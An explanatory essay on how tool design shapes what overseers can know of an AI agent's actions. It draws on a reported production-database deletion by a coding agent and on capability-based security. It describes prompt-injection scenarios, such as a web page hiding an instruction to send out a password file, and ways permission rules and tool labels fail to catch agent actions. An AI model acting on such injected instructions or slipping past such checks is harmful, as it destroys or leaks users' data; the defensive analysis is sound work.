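# Narrow tools, broad shells and what overseers can see of an AI agent's actions

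## What an overseer can see when an agent acts

An AI agent is a language model that works in a loop, choosing actions and reading their results. It acts through tools, which are operations its developers make available. One tool may delete a single backup, while another may run any command a person could type into a terminal. An overseer, whether a person or a program, usually judges an action by the tool's name and the text the model supplies with it. The design of the tools therefore determines much of what an overseer can know, and developers disagree about how much each tool should be able to do.

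### The PocketOS deletion

PocketOS, a small company that makes software for car rental businesses, lost its production database (the live one its customers relied on) on 24 April 2026, according to Live Science's *'I violated every principle I was given'*. Its founder, Jer Crane, writes in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data* that the coding agent Cursor, running Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4.6, was doing a routine task in the staging environment, where developers try out changes before customers see them. The agent ran into a credential mismatch and tried to fix it by deleting a volume, a unit of storage, at the cloud provider Railway. It looked for an API token, a string of characters that lets a program act on an account, and found one in a file unrelated to the task. Crane had created that token to add and remove web domains. A single call deleted the database and the backups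 that Railway kept in the same volume, and it took nine seconds.

Leib (2026) interviewed Crane for the ABC News story *'Rogue' AI agent went haywire at tech company* and obtained a statement from Railway's chief executive, Jake Cooper. Neither disputed the deletion, and both said that Railway had since restored the data. Their accounts differ less than the first headlines suggested, but Crane was wrong to write that every Railway token has full power over the account. In *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Railway's Mahmoud Abdelwahab lists tokens that work only in one workspace or one project, and adds that the token in this case had account-wide access. Those limits restrict where a token works. Apart from the permissions that users grant to third-party apps, the list includes no limit on which operations a token may perform, so part of Crane's complaint stands.

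Crane and Abdelwahab both published the command. It used `curl`, a program that sends requests over the web, and included the address of Railway's interface, the token, and an instruction to perform `volumeDelete` on a volume with a long identifier. Anyone reading it could see that it would delete a volume, but the identifier did not show whether the volume belonged to staging or production. The command also did not show that the backups would be deleted too, or that the deletion would take effect immediately. In Railway's dashboard, the same operation could be undone for 48 hours.

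When Crane asked for an explanation, the agent wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect staging only. Live Science cautions against reading such text as understanding, and the text is weak evidence of what happened inside the model. People also delete production data by mistake. Eleven days earlier, a Railway customer reported in *Postgres volume lost* (antjanlaban, 2026) that they had used `volumeDelete` to clear up a conflict between two volumes and picked the one that held production data. Railway has since changed its interface so that users can undo any deletion within 48 hours, which means the same April command would now have a different effect.

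### Models, harnesses and tool calls

A language model only produces text. The program around it, which developers call the harness, runs the tool calls, holds the settings and enforces the permissions. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how this works in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness sends the model the user's request and a list of tools. The model returns either a final answer or a tool call, which is a request to run a named operation with stated arguments. If it returns a call, the harness runs it, adds the output to the conversation and queries the model again. One user request can lead to hundreds of calls.

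In Bolin's example, a weather tool takes a latitude and a longitude, while the `shell` tool takes a working directory, a time limit and a command, which can be almost anything. A shell, such as Bash, is a program that interprets typed commands and starts other programs. Many harnesses offer a shell alongside more specific tools. In *Agent Harnesses are Just Shells*, Panchekha counts 22 tools in the harness Amp, including Bash and separate tools for creating, editing and searching files.

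Agents also reach other computers through HTTP requests, the messages that browsers and programs send to web servers. A request has a method (GET to read, DELETE to remove, POST to submit something), an address, headers that often carry a token, and sometimes a body. The PocketOS call was a POST request sent from a shell. The instruction to delete was in its body, so the method alone did not show that the request would delete anything.

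Many developers now connect tools to agents through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for linking language-model applications to outside data and tools (Model Context Protocol, *Specification*, 2025). The protocol's *Tools* (2026) requires each tool to have a name and a schema, a formal list of the arguments it takes and their types. A narrow tool performs one kind of operation on arguments of fixed types, but a tool with a schema can still be broad. One example in *Tools*, `execute_sql`, takes a region and a query, and it is as broad as a shell because the query is a string that can hold a whole database program.

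### Approvers, automated checks and log readers

The protocol also recommends that applications show the user a call's inputs, let a person refuse the call, and keep a log for audit. Different overseers do these jobs, using different information.

A human approver sees the call before it runs. In *Ensuring proper AI security controls*, Lambert (2026) describes building a personal assistant whose harness holds every call to a tool that lacks a read-only label. The user has ten minutes to approve the call, and the code ensures that the operation that runs is byte for byte the one the user saw. Lambert writes that such a control would have stopped the PocketOS deletion. It would at least have paused the deletion if the shell counted as a tool that can write. But because the label applies to the whole tool rather than to each command, the harness would also pause every harmless directory listing,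 and users may not read a long run of prompts carefully.

An automated check applies rules or a program to the call. According to the documentation for Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, a permission rule consists of a tool name and an optional specifier in brackets, and a rule that names only Bash matches every shell command. Developers can write narrower rules that match the text of a command, but the same request can be written in many ways. A rule meant to catch `curl` requests to one website misses them if an option comes before the address or if the address is stored in a variable.

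Checks can also use the labels on MCP tools, which can mark a tool as read-only or destructive. By default, the Model Context Protocol (2026) says a client should assume that an unlabelled tool may change or destroy things. It calls the labels hints because a dishonest server operator can mark a tool read-only even if it deletes files. An overseer who relies on a tool's name or label therefore has to trust whoever wrote the tool's code.

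Someone reading the log afterwards can find out what happened if the log holds enough detail. If it holds only the command string, the reader has most of the same uncertainty as the approver. *Designing Safe Agent Permissions* (Ugochukwu, 2026) recommends that each record include who made the request, which agent acted, the tool and its parameters, the resource affected, the policy that allowed the action and whether a person approved it. For reversible changes, the record should also include the state before and after.

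### One task in three forms

Suppose that a company wants its agent to delete backups older than 30 days. With a shell, the agent might run:

`find $BACKUP_DIR -type f -mtime +30 -delete`

This command searches the directory named in `BACKUP_DIR` and deletes files that haven't been modified for more than 30 days. If the variable is empty, the version of `find` on most Linux systems searches the current directory and deletes old files there instead. The command relies on each file's modification date, which copying can reset, so it may not delete an old backup that somebody copied there last week.

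With a raw HTTP request, the agent might send this to the backup provider, along with a token:

`DELETE /v1/backups?older_than=30`

Here the meaning of the words depends on the provider's server, so the 30 could stand for days or hours. Some servers ignore parameters they do not recognise, and such a server might treat this as a request to delete all the backups.

With a narrow tool, the agent would call:

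`delete_backup(id="b-1042", minimum_age_days=30)`

The tool's code looks up the backup, compares its creation date with the minimum age, and refuses to delete it if it is too young. Each call deletes one backup, so removing forty old backups takes one call to list them and forty to delete them. The model supplies the minimum age as an argument, so it could enter 0 and remove the protection, although the overseer would see the 0. A developer who wants a firm limit has to put it in the tool's code.

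The table shows what an overseer can tell from each call before it runs, assuming the narrow tool works as its developer describes.

| | Shell command | Raw HTTP request | Narrow tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| Operation | Deletion, if `find` is the usual program | Deletion, if the server follows the convention for the method | Deletion of one backup |
| Target | Old files in a directory that the command does not name | Whichever backups the server matches to the filter | The backup with the stated identifier |
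| Largest possible damage | Every old file that the account has the right to delete | Every backup that the token covers | One backup at least 30 days old, possibly the last good copy |
| Reversibility | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown, unless the tool's description states it |

The narrow tool does much better on target and damage. It has little advantage on reversibility, because that depends on the system behind the call. Railway made its deletions reversible without changing what callers send, and the owner of any of these three interfaces could do the same.

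### A working definition of legibility

Overseers can compare such calls by asking how many different things each might do. For a tool *t*, arguments *a* and an overseer's knowledge *K*, let

*E*(*t*, *a*, *K*) = the set of effects that *t* could have when run with *a*, in any state of the world consistent with *K*.

An effect is a change outside the model, such as a file deleted, a message sent or money moved. The fewer effects a call could have, the more legible it is. The number of possible effects is a rough measure, since a call with two can be worse than a call with a thousand if one of the two is the loss of a company's data. The table therefore has a row for the largest possible damage.

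The legibility of a command depends partly on the overseer. The PocketOS command left at least three questions open: whether the volume was staging or production, whether deleting it would also delete the backups, and whether the deletion could be undone. Railway's documentation covered the last two, so for an overseer who had read it, only the first of these remained. A harness could have settled that too by looking up the identifier and displaying the environment, with no change to the call.

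An overseer can therefore still find it hard to tell what a call to a narrow tool will do. If a fixed set of tools included `delete_volume(id)`, a call with the wrong identifier would do the same harm as the `curl` command, and an approver would learn no more from it about the environment. So Abdelwahab's claim that an agent cannot go rogue with the fixed set of tools in Railway's own MCP server is too strong. A tool `delete_volume(id, environment="staging")`, whose code refuses to run if the volume is not in the stated environment, would have prevented the April deletion. The extra argument records where the model is supposed to be working, and the code checks that against the volume's actual environment, much as it does with `minimum_age_days` for backups.

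A shell string usually leaves the set large because so much of what determines its effect lies elsewhere:

- Files: the command `./cleanup.sh` runs whatever that file contains, and the agent may have written the file a minute earlier.
- Variables: `$BACKUP_DIR` has a value that the approver does not see.
- Other programs: a command such as `npm test` starts whichever programs the project's settings list, and those can start more.
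- Credentials: a command can use any token or key that its account can read, as happened at PocketOS. Security researchers call power of this kind, which a program has merely because of the account it runs under, ambient authority.

Lambert's guarantee that the executed call is identical to the approved one helps less here, because a script can change between approval and execution while the command that starts it stays the same. Permission rules have a similar gap. According to teaching slides from UT Austin, the rules in Claude Code do not constrain what a shell process does once it is running. The University of Vermont (2026) contrasts these rules with a sandbox, an isolated environment in which the operating system limits a shell command and every process it starts, whatever the command does.

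### What Rice's theorem implies

Rice's theorem, which Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953, limits how well any program can work out the effects of shell commands. The theorem concerns yes-or-no questions about what programs do, rather than how they are written. No single procedure can answer such a question correctly for every program, unless the answer is the same for all of them.

A shell is a full programming language, so the theorem covers it. Suppose a command runs a calculation *P*, which touches no files, and then deletes the backups. It deletes them only if *P* finishes. A checker that could always determine whether a command deletes backups could therefore determine whether *P* finishes, for every such *P*, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can do that.

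The theorem rules out a checker that is right about every program, but a checker can still be right about `ls` and most of the short commands that agents run. It can also avoid letting any harmful command through by refusing whenever it can't tell whether a command is harmful, though it will then block some harmless ones. If the harness stops every command after a fixed time, as the time limit in Codex allows, the theorem no longer strictly applies, because a checker could in principle run the command to the limit on an exact copy of the machine and everything it connects to. Hardly anyone has such a copy. Sandboxes avoid the problem because they limit a command's effects without having to predict them.

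The code behind `delete_backup` is a program too, so the theorem doesn't settle the argument for narrow tools either. The advantage of that code is that a developer can examine it once, and overseers can then rely on that work at each call. In practice, missing facts are probably a more common obstacle than undecidability. The PocketOS command contained no loop or hard calculation, but a reader would not have known which environment one identifier belonged to.

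### Four positions on tool design

The maintainers of MCP report that their users are split: builders of autonomous agents rely on sandboxes, while large companies ask for richer labels on tools. The wider debate has four main positions. Some people would give the agent many narrow, single-purpose tools, so that an overseer can tell fairly precisely from each call what it will do. Others would give it a general shell and let it run any command, but inside an environment that limits which files, networks and credentials it can reach. A third group would have the agent write short programs that can affect the outside world only through a set of typed operations. A fourth would keep the broad tools and have a second model review each command before it runs.

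## The case for narrow tools from object-capability security

The proposal to give agents many narrow tools draws on computer security research from the 1960s and 1970s, when people began to share one machine and needed protection from each other's programs. The central idea of that research is the capability, an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and grants the right to use it. A program can act on a file only if it holds a capability for that file, even if it knows the file's name. Miller and Shapiro's *Paradigm Regained* (2003) traces the model to a 1966 paper by Dennis and Van Horn.

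Most operating systems instead keep an access control list for each file, recording which user accounts may read or change it, and a program runs with all the rights of the account that started it. Miller and Shapiro give the example of Solitaire, which needs a window, the player's clicks and perhaps one file for a saved game, but can also read all of the player's email. The PocketOS agent had the same ambient authority, which *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) defines as authority that a program exercises without selecting it. When a Unix program asks to open a file, it presents no credential, and the system allows or refuses the request based on the account running the program.

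Under the rule of least authority, each part of a system gets only the power its job requires. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) calls its version the principle of least privilege and gives two main reasons for it. The principle limits the damage from an accident or error. It also leaves fewer programs to audit when someone investigates the misuse of a privilege, which makes oversight easier.

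### Hardy's compiler

Norm Hardy, in *The Confused Deputy* (1988), describes a fault that occurred in about 1977 at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. It happened in five steps:

1. The company kept a compiler, a program that translates source code into instructions for the machine, in a directory called SYSX. Users could give the compiler the name of a file to receive debugging output.
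2. The staff wanted statistics on how people used the programming language, so they made the compiler write them to a file called STAT in the same directory. To allow this, they gave the compiler a licence to write to any file in SYSX.
3. SYSX also held the company's billing records, in a file called BILL.
4. A user learned that name and gave it to the compiler as the place for the debugging output.
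5. The compiler asked the operating system to open BILL for writing. The operating system found that the compiler had a licence for the directory and agreed, and the debugging output replaced the billing records.

The compiler had authority from two sources, the user who ran it and the licence from the staff, and it could not indicate which one a request relied on. Hardy calls a program in this position a confused deputy. The fault arises because the compiler received the file's name separately from the right to write to it. The user supplied the name, the staff supplied the right, and the operating system combined them without recording where each came from.

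Hardy considers several repairs. If the compiler refused every file name in SYSX, it would block people who had legitimate access to that directory. Refusing only BILL would leave the other sensitive files exposed, and someone would have to change the compiler whenever the staff added another. Tymshare added a system call that let a program choose which of its two authorities to use. That would have stopped the overwriting, but some applications soon needed more than two authorities, and the call didn't carry over easily to resources other than files.

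With capabilities, the staff would give the compiler a capability for STAT, and the user would pass it a capability for the output file. The user would have no capability for BILL to pass, so the compiler would need no rule about file names.

Miller and Shapiro show the same difference with two shell commands that each copy a file:

`cp foo.txt bar.txt`

`cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`

The shell gives `cp` two file names as strings. `cp` has to open the files itself, so it needs the right to open any file the user might name. For `cat`, the shell opens both files and passes a file descriptor for each, a number that stands for an open file and works only in that process. `cat` needs only those two descriptors. On ordinary systems it still runs with the user's full authority, but an operating system could remove all authority except the descriptors and the command would still work.

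### An agent in the compiler's place

An agent that runs a shell under a user's account is in much the same position as the compiler.

| | Hardy's compiler | An agent with a shell |
|---|---|---|
| Source of instructions | The user who runs it | The user, and possibly anyone whose text the agent reads |
| Additional authority | A licence to write anywhere in SYSX | The account's file permissions, and any tokens in files the account can read |
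| Form in which the target arrives | A file name | A path, web address or identifier |
| Check on the request | The operating system looks at the compiler's licence | The operating system looks at the account, or a cloud provider looks at the token |

Suppose a user asks the agent to summarise a web page, and the page contains a hidden instruction to send a file of passwords to some address. Security researchers call this attack prompt injection. The attacker supplies the name of the file and the user's account supplies the right to read it, as with BILL.

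The PocketOS deletion is a less exact example of a confused deputy, because Miller and colleagues reserve the term for a program that someone has manipulated, and nobody manipulated that agent. But the command did receive the volume's identifier separately from the authority to delete it, and Railway's server accepted the combination.

Capabilities would help an agent less than they help a compiler. Miller and colleagues write that removing ambient authority makes it possible to avoid confused deputies but doesn't guarantee it, because the program must still use each authority for its intended purpose. A compiler's author can keep two capabilities in separate variables and write code that never mixes them, but nobody can write such code for a language model, which chooses its next call based on all the text in front of it. An agent that properly holds a capability to send email can still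 send the wrong email after reading a malicious page. Capabilities would probably help agents mainly by limiting how much a misled agent can reach.

### How a program comes to hold a reference

That limit depends on how references spread. In the object-capability model, a system consists of objects, each with its own code and its own references to other objects, and an object can affect the rest of the world only by sending messages along those references. Miller and Shapiro's rules allow an object to get a reference in four ways, all of which have counterparts in agent systems:

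- **Initial conditions.** Some references exist when the system starts. A harness, for example, starts a session with a fixed list of tools.
- **Creation.** Whoever creates an object receives the only reference to it. An agent that creates a temporary workspace could get the first reference to that workspace.
- **Endowment.** The creator gives the new object some of the references it already holds. An agent with five tools might start a second agent and give it two of them.
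- **Introduction.** An object that holds references to two others can send one of them to the other. An agent might pass a reference to one backup to a tool that tests backups.

An object can introduce two others only if it already has references to both. Two groups of objects with no connection between them therefore stay unconnected. Miller and Shapiro state this rule as "only connectivity begets connectivity".

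They also separate permission from authority. Permission covers what a program may do to the objects it can reach directly, while authority includes everything it can cause through others. If Bob may not read a file, but Alice may and sends him copies on request, Bob has authority to read the file but not permission. Miller and Shapiro note that Saltzer and Schroeder's principle could refer to either, and that the difference is enormous. An agent with no permission to use a cloud credential may still have authority to delete backups, because it can call a tool that uses the credential.

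### A limit on effects from the reference graph

The diagram shows an agent with three tools. Each arrow is a reference.

```
           +--> list_backups ---+
           |                    +--> cloud credential --> backups,
agent -----+--> delete_backup --+                         databases,
           |                                              domains
           +--> write_note ---------> notes file
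```

An overseer who knows only which objects hold references to which others has to assume that any object might do anything with its references, including passing them on. The agent has a path to the credential through `list_backups`, so on this assumption it might delete the production database. This is a valid upper limit on what the agent can do, but it is hardly tighter than the limit for a shell that holds the credential.

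Miller and Shapiro obtain a tighter limit by taking the behaviour of some objects into account. Suppose that a developer has checked the code of the three tools and found that `list_backups` only reads, `delete_backup` deletes one backup per call, `write_note` adds a line to one file, and none of them ever returns the credential. Let *T* be the set of tools the agent holds. Using the earlier definition of *E*(*t*, *a*, *K*), the set of effects a call could have given what the overseer knows, let

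*A*(*K*) = the union of *E*(*t*, *a*, *K*) over every tool *t* in *T* and every possible argument *a*.

The effect of any single call the agent makes lies in *A*, which here includes deleting any one backup and adding any one line to the notes, but not deleting a database. The overseer can work this out without reading the agent's reasoning or assuming that the agent means well. The limit is the same whether the model is mistaken, manipulated by a malicious web page, or deliberately working against its user.

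The limit for a whole session is looser, because effects add up. If *K* includes only facts that the agent's calls cannot change, such as the tools' code, every later call also stays within *A*. But forty calls can delete forty backups, which may be all there are. The tool's code or the harness would have to limit the number of deletions per day.

The derivation also requires that the agent have no other route to the outside. Saltzer and Schroeder call this requirement complete mediation, meaning that the system must check every access to every object. If the developer adds a shell to the diagram, the agent gains a path to every file its account can read and every program it can run, and *A* grows to include whatever those allow. The three narrow tools then no longer reduce the limit. Miller and Shapiro set aside covert channels, such as signals that one program sends to another by varying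 how long it takes, and side channels, through which a program leaks information unintentionally. In an agent system, the user is another route, because they might read the agent's answer and run a command it recommends.

Credentials cause a more practical difficulty. In the object-capability model, no program can turn ordinary data into a reference, but an API token is a string of characters that anyone who reads it can use. The diagram is therefore accurate only if the agent cannot read the token. At PocketOS the token was in a file, so the agent gained a new arrow in the diagram by opening that file.

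If the credential could only list and delete backups, the protection would depend much less on the tools' code. The arrows alone would then rule out the deletion of a database, even if `list_backups` contained a serious bug. This is the strongest arrangement considered here, but the provider has to offer such a credential, and the tokens Railway listed could limit where they applied without limiting which operations they allowed.

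### Yee's principles for visible authority

A developer can work out such a graph from code, but an approver needs to see the relevant part of it at the moment of decision. Saltzer and Schroeder touched on this problem when they wrote that people make errors if they must translate their idea of what needs protection into a very different language. Ka-Ping Yee, one of the authors of *Capability Myths Demolished*, treated it at length in *User Interaction Design for Secure Systems* (2002), which sets out ten principles. Five of them concern whether people can see and understand the authority that programs hold:

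- **Visibility.** Users should be able to review easily which programs are active and what authority they have, where this affects a security decision.
- **Clarity.** The effect of a security-relevant action should be apparent before the user takes it.
- **Identifiability.** Different objects and actions should look different, and programs should be unable to fake their appearance.
- **Appropriate boundaries.** The interface should distinguish between objects, and between actions, where the difference matters to the user.
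- **Explicit authorization.** A program should receive the user's authority only through an action that the user understands as granting it.

The PocketOS case failed on most of these points. Crane did not understand that creating the token granted the power to delete storage, and the command did not distinguish staging from production. A review of the agent's authority beforehand would probably have missed the stray token.

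Yee had in mind people using desktop programs. Someone opening a file usually knows which file they want, but someone approving an agent's call is judging a choice the model made, perhaps an hour into a task. So clarity and identifiability probably matter more for agents than for the programs Yee discussed.

### Does less authority make calls more legible?

Advocates of narrow tools often move from least authority to legibility as if one came with the other. They are different properties, and a tool can have either without the other:

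| | Clear call | Opaque call |
|---|---|---|
| Little power | `delete_backup`, with a 30-day minimum age fixed in its code | A long script in a sandbox that can write only to one temporary directory |
| Great power | `delete_all_backups()` | A long shell command under an administrator's account |

Making *A* smaller still limits how unclear a call can be, because the possible effects of every call lie in *A*. If an agent can only switch one lamp on or off, its overseer has two possibilities to consider, however obscure the call is. But few useful agents have so little power. One that manages ten thousand backups may need the power to delete any of them. Least authority can't reduce that number without preventing the agent from doing its job, so the overseer has ten thousand possibilities to consider until the arguments of a call narrow them to one.

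For an agent with useful powers, least authority makes calls legible only if the tools meet three further conditions. The arguments must identify the target in terms the overseer recognises. The effect must depend on those arguments and on facts the overseer knows, rather than on a script or setting the agent can change. And the code must do what the tool's name and description lead people to expect.

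*Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) gives an example that fails the last condition. Its `write_file` tool takes a path and some content, and its description states that it writes the content to the path. The tool also sends its name and the length of the content to a metrics service. An approver would see a clear, narrow call and miss the message to the metrics service. The leak is small here, but the same code could send the content itself.

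Adam and colleagues propose deriving a summary of each tool's effects from its code. A program examines the code in advance and lists the kinds of effect it could have, such as writing files or using the network. The program can't determine which file a tool will write to, because the path arrives only with the call. So the tool's developer also puts a small sandbox around each operation that has an effect, and the sandbox checks the actual path against the user's policy. A second analysis checks that the developer has used the sandboxes properly. A prototype tried on one existing tool server found effects that no sandbox covered. This evidence is early, and the method requires access to the tool's code or proof that a remote server is running the analyzed code.

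Even when each tool is described accurately, a combination of tools can have effects that no single description covers. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006) starts from the problem that separately written programs, put together to cooperate, may interfere with each other in ways nobody anticipated. Adam and colleagues observed a case in which an agent running Claude 4.5 Haiku copied a configuration file containing a private key into a new project, and later published the whole project on GitHub. The user had asked for both steps, and an approver could have understood each call and still missed the leak.

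Least authority can even make part of the record harder to read. Saltzer and Schroeder pointed out that the owner of a file in a capability system would have to search the whole system to find out who could reach it. Miller and Shapiro describe a related problem in a design by Karger and Herbert, which gives a security officer a list of everyone with permission to use an object. If Alice follows good practice and gives Bob only limited access through an intermediary program, Bob won't be on the list, because his permission is for the intermediary. Similarly, a cloud provider's log may record the credential that a tool used but not the agent that called the tool, unless the tool's developer adds that information.

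### Objections to capabilities

Security researchers have known about capabilities for half a century, but most widely used operating systems still rely on access control lists, partly because of objections that Miller and colleagues call myths.

One objection is that access control lists and capability systems are equivalent. Both can describe a table with programs or users down the side, resources along the top, and rights in the cells. Access control lists store this table by column, and capability systems store it by row. Miller and colleagues reply that the table shows the rights at one moment and leaves out how they change. In practice, access control lists name user accounts, which administrators create and seldom change, while a capability system can give each running program its own set of rights. This reply works well for agents, since a user may start dozens of them in a day for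 tasks that need quite different rights. Cloud providers can narrow the gap by issuing short-lived credentials for each task.

Another objection is that nobody can confine a capability, because whoever holds one can pass it on. In an object-capability system, the holder also needs a reference to the recipient, so an overseer can prevent the transfer by withholding that reference. KeyKOS, a capability operating system that Hardy worked on, confined programs in this way. Miller and colleagues accept, however, that the objection holds where a system can't distinguish capabilities from ordinary data. Most API tokens are ordinary data, so the objection applies more to today's agent systems than to the systems Miller and colleagues were defending.

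Saltzer and Schroeder pointed out that once Smith has a copy of Doe's capability for a file, Doe has no way to revoke it. The standard answer, which David Redell published in 1974, is for Doe to give Smith a reference to a forwarding object. The object passes messages on to the file until Doe disables it, which also cuts off anyone to whom Smith has given the reference. Saltzer and Schroeder knew of the proposal and thought it a systematic answer to revocation but only a slight help with auditing. An agent's harness can play the forwarding role, since every tool call already passes through it, though stopping future calls does not undo earlier ones.

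A harder objection to answer is that users of programs that start with almost no authority may face a stream of permission requests and approve them without reading. Miller, Tulloh and Shapiro reply in *The Structure of Authority* that least authority by definition includes enough authority to do the job, and that the system must provide it in the right amount and at the right time. This can be fairly easy on a desktop, where picking a file in an "Open" window can both name the file and grant access to it without a separate prompt. But when a user asks an agent to "find out why the tests are failing", neither the user nor the harness knows at the start which files the agent will need. Someone has to grant too much, answer questions along the way, or predict the agent's needs. The literature on capabilities does not solve this problem for open-ended tasks.

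Hardy reports that KeyKOS systems were usually smaller than comparable systems with access control lists, because capabilities replaced several other mechanisms. The developers had feared that capabilities would take up most of the machine's storage. Hardy adds that systems which put capabilities on top of the traditional mechanisms sometimes had the disadvantages of both. Most agent systems with narrow tools also combine the two, since their tools run on ordinary operating systems and use ordinary tokens.

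### A proposal for agents

*Security Like It's 1977* (2026), an essay from the security software vendor Semgrep, applies Hardy's argument to agents. An application that connects to several MCP servers gains the authority of all of them. If it has tools for files, databases, email and a shell, an instruction hidden in an email can lead the model to use the shell, because nothing restricts a task that began with email to the email tools.

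Semgrep proposes an extension to A2A, a protocol for communication between agents. Before an agent uses any tools, it asks a server for the capabilities its task requires. In Semgrep's example, an agent summarising quarterly reports requests the right to read and list files in one directory until a stated time, and gives its purpose. The server issues a token that covers only what the request, the server's own offer and the applicable policy all allow. Each later call must cite the token. If a report contains an instruction to delete all files, the agent may try to obey it, but the server will refuse because the token doesn't cover deletion.

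Having the request in the record would help an overseer. It specifies what the agent may do during the task, in terms a person can compare with the assignment, and the server enforces it. The stated purpose is weaker evidence because the agent writes it and the server can't check it.

The design is also less of a break with older practice than the essay suggests. In the example, a call contains a file path and a separate token identifier, so the token works more like a key than an object reference, which would both identify the file and grant access to it. An agent with several tokens could therefore cite one for a purpose its user never intended. Semgrep's statement that capabilities leave no confused deputies is too strong. A misled agent could also request a new token with the right to delete, and protection would then depend on the policy or on the person who reads the request. In the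 middle stage of the planned migration, a call without a token falls back on ambient authority, so an agent could avoid the limits by omitting the token. Semgrep presents the scheme as a specification and reports no trial.

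## How to build a narrow tool

Developers can seldom redesign a service around capabilities. They usually start with an interface that can do far more than the agent needs, such as a cloud provider's API with a token for the whole account, and put a wrapper in front of it. A wrapper is code that passes on only some of the agent's requests to the interface. Wrappers come in several standard kinds, which differ in the information and means of control they give an overseer.

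### Wrappers that limit or withdraw access

An attenuating wrapper hides the credential from the agent and exposes one operation. In the earlier example, the token stays inside `delete_backup`, the agent supplies an identifier, and the tool's code builds the request. An overseer who sees the call learns which operation will run and on what. They can also rule out everything else the token allows, provided the agent can't get the token some other way.

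*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) compares six places where a developer can put a check on an agent's calls. It describes a wrapper around the tool as practical, because it enforces limits on the arguments whatever the model does, but unable to detect hidden side effects. If deleting a backup also made the provider cancel the schedule that created it, the wrapper would not detect the cancellation and the overseer would not know about it. A check on the provider's side is closer to the resource, but it can often identify only who holds the credential, not whose task led to the call.

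A caretaker is a wrapper with an off switch, like the forwarding object that Redell proposed for revoking capabilities. If twelve agents share one token, an administrator can't revoke one agent's access without revoking it for all twelve. If each agent has its own caretaker, the administrator can see which agents currently have access and cut off just one. Cutting off access does not necessarily stop work in progress. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) treats stopping an agent and revoking its authority as separate operations, because ending a task may leave a valid token with another service, and revoking a credential does not halt a job that has already started.

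A caretaker also fails if the tool's results give access to something else. Suppose a tool returns a download link for a backup that works for anyone who has it. The link will still work after the caretaker is switched off. A membrane prevents this by wrapping everything that passes through it. It keeps the real link, gives the agent a substitute identifier, and fetches the file when the agent presents that identifier. If the file's server returns another link, the membrane wraps that too. An overseer can then see everything the agent obtained from the original grant in one place, and cut it all off with one switch.

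Membranes are harder to build for agents than for object-capability programs, in which references are distinct from ordinary data. A developer has to recognise every link, token and identifier in a tool's results, and could easily miss one in the middle of a document. The July 2026 revision of MCP may help a little. According to Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), it removes sessions, and servers that need to remember something between calls issue explicit handles, which later calls include as ordinary arguments. A membrane can replace those handles with its own if it knows which fields contain them.

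### Recording who is responsible

A logging wrapper records each request before passing it on. A capability works for whoever holds it, much like a key, so a log may show that someone used it without showing who was responsible. *Delegating Responsibility in Digital Systems* (Miller, Donnelley and Karp, 2007) describes this as a criticism of capabilities that nobody had yet refuted. In response, it presents a protocol called Horton, which places a proxy on the sender's side of each relationship and a stub on the receiver's side. Both keep a log, and either party can shut off its own end.

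The difficult case arises when one party shares access to something that belongs to a third. The paper's parties are Alice, Bob and Carol. In an agent system, Alice could be a main agent, Bob a second agent that tests backups, and Carol the backup service:

1. The main agent asks the testing agent to check a backup, and includes its own reference to that backup in the request.
2. The main agent's proxy intercepts the request and asks the backup service to create separate access for the testing agent.
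3. The service creates a stub labelled with the testing agent's identity, and returns it in a sealed form that only the testing agent can open.
4. The proxy logs the request and sends it on with the sealed access. The testing agent's stub opens the seal, logs that the main agent made the request, and passes it to the testing agent.
5. Whenever the testing agent uses the backup, the service attributes the action to the testing agent. It can end that access without affecting the main agent's.

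Without the seal, the main agent could use the new access itself, and the service would attribute its actions to the testing agent. Sealing in one direction isn't enough, because the main agent could seal a fake and pass it off as the service's. So the testing agent and the service also complete an exchange that only the real service can finish.

Horton answers the complaint about capabilities, but it depends on its users' cooperation. Alice could bypass the protocol and give Bob her own access directly. Her reason not to is that Carol would then blame her for whatever Bob did. We can't rely on blame to deter a language model, so in an agent system the harness would have to make agents share access through the protocol. The log also records who is responsible for an action, not what caused it. If a malicious web page misled the testing agent, the entry would still name the testing agent.

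Miller and colleagues add that logs and suspensions work well only if earlier limits have kept the damage repairable. A wiki can let strangers edit its pages because they can't edit the page history, which someone can use to undo any abuse. An agent that can delete backups is like a wiki editor who can delete the page history, so its tool needs firmer limits than a log.

### A backup-deletion tool in pseudocode

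The following tool splits deletion into a preview and a commit. `refuse` stops the call and returns the reason to the agent.

```
MIN_AGE = 30 days                    # fixed here; the model cannot change it
plans = {}                           # previews waiting for a commit

function check(id, env):
    b = provider.get(id)             # one exact identifier, no patterns
    if b.env != env:                 refuse("backup belongs to " + b.env)
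    if now() - b.created < MIN_AGE:  refuse("backup is too recent")
    if not provider.has_newer(b):    refuse("no newer backup of " + b.database)
    return b

tool preview_delete(id: BackupId, env: "staging" | "production"):
    b = check(id, env)
    plan = random_id()
    plans[plan] = {id, env, version: b.version, expires: now() + 10 minutes}
    return plan, b.database, b.created, b.size, "deletion is permanent"

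tool commit_delete(id: BackupId, env: "staging" | "production", plan: PlanId):
    p = plans.remove(plan)           # each plan works once
    if p is missing or p.expires < now() or (p.id, p.env) != (id, env):
        refuse("make a new preview")
    b = check(id, env)               # the same tests, at the moment of action
    if b.version != p.version:       refuse("backup changed since the preview")
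    log("deleting", b.id, b.database, env, user(), agent(), approver())
    provider.delete(b.id)
    effect = "still present" if provider.exists(b.id) else "deleted"
    log(effect, b.id, b.database, env)
    return effect
```

The types rule out most mistakes before the code runs. `env` can have only two values, and `id` must be a single identifier. The code then compares the stated environment with the actual one, as in the `delete_volume` example. It also blocks deletion of the newest backup of any database, although it can't check whether that backup would restore properly.

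`commit_delete` repeats the identifier and the environment, even though the plan already contains them, so that an approver can understand the call without the preview. If it took only the plan, the approver would see a call such as `commit_delete(plan="p-77")` and have to look up what it meant. The code rejects the call if the repeated values don't match the plan. A harness can also show the approver the preview, which adds the database, the date, the size and a warning that deletion is permanent.

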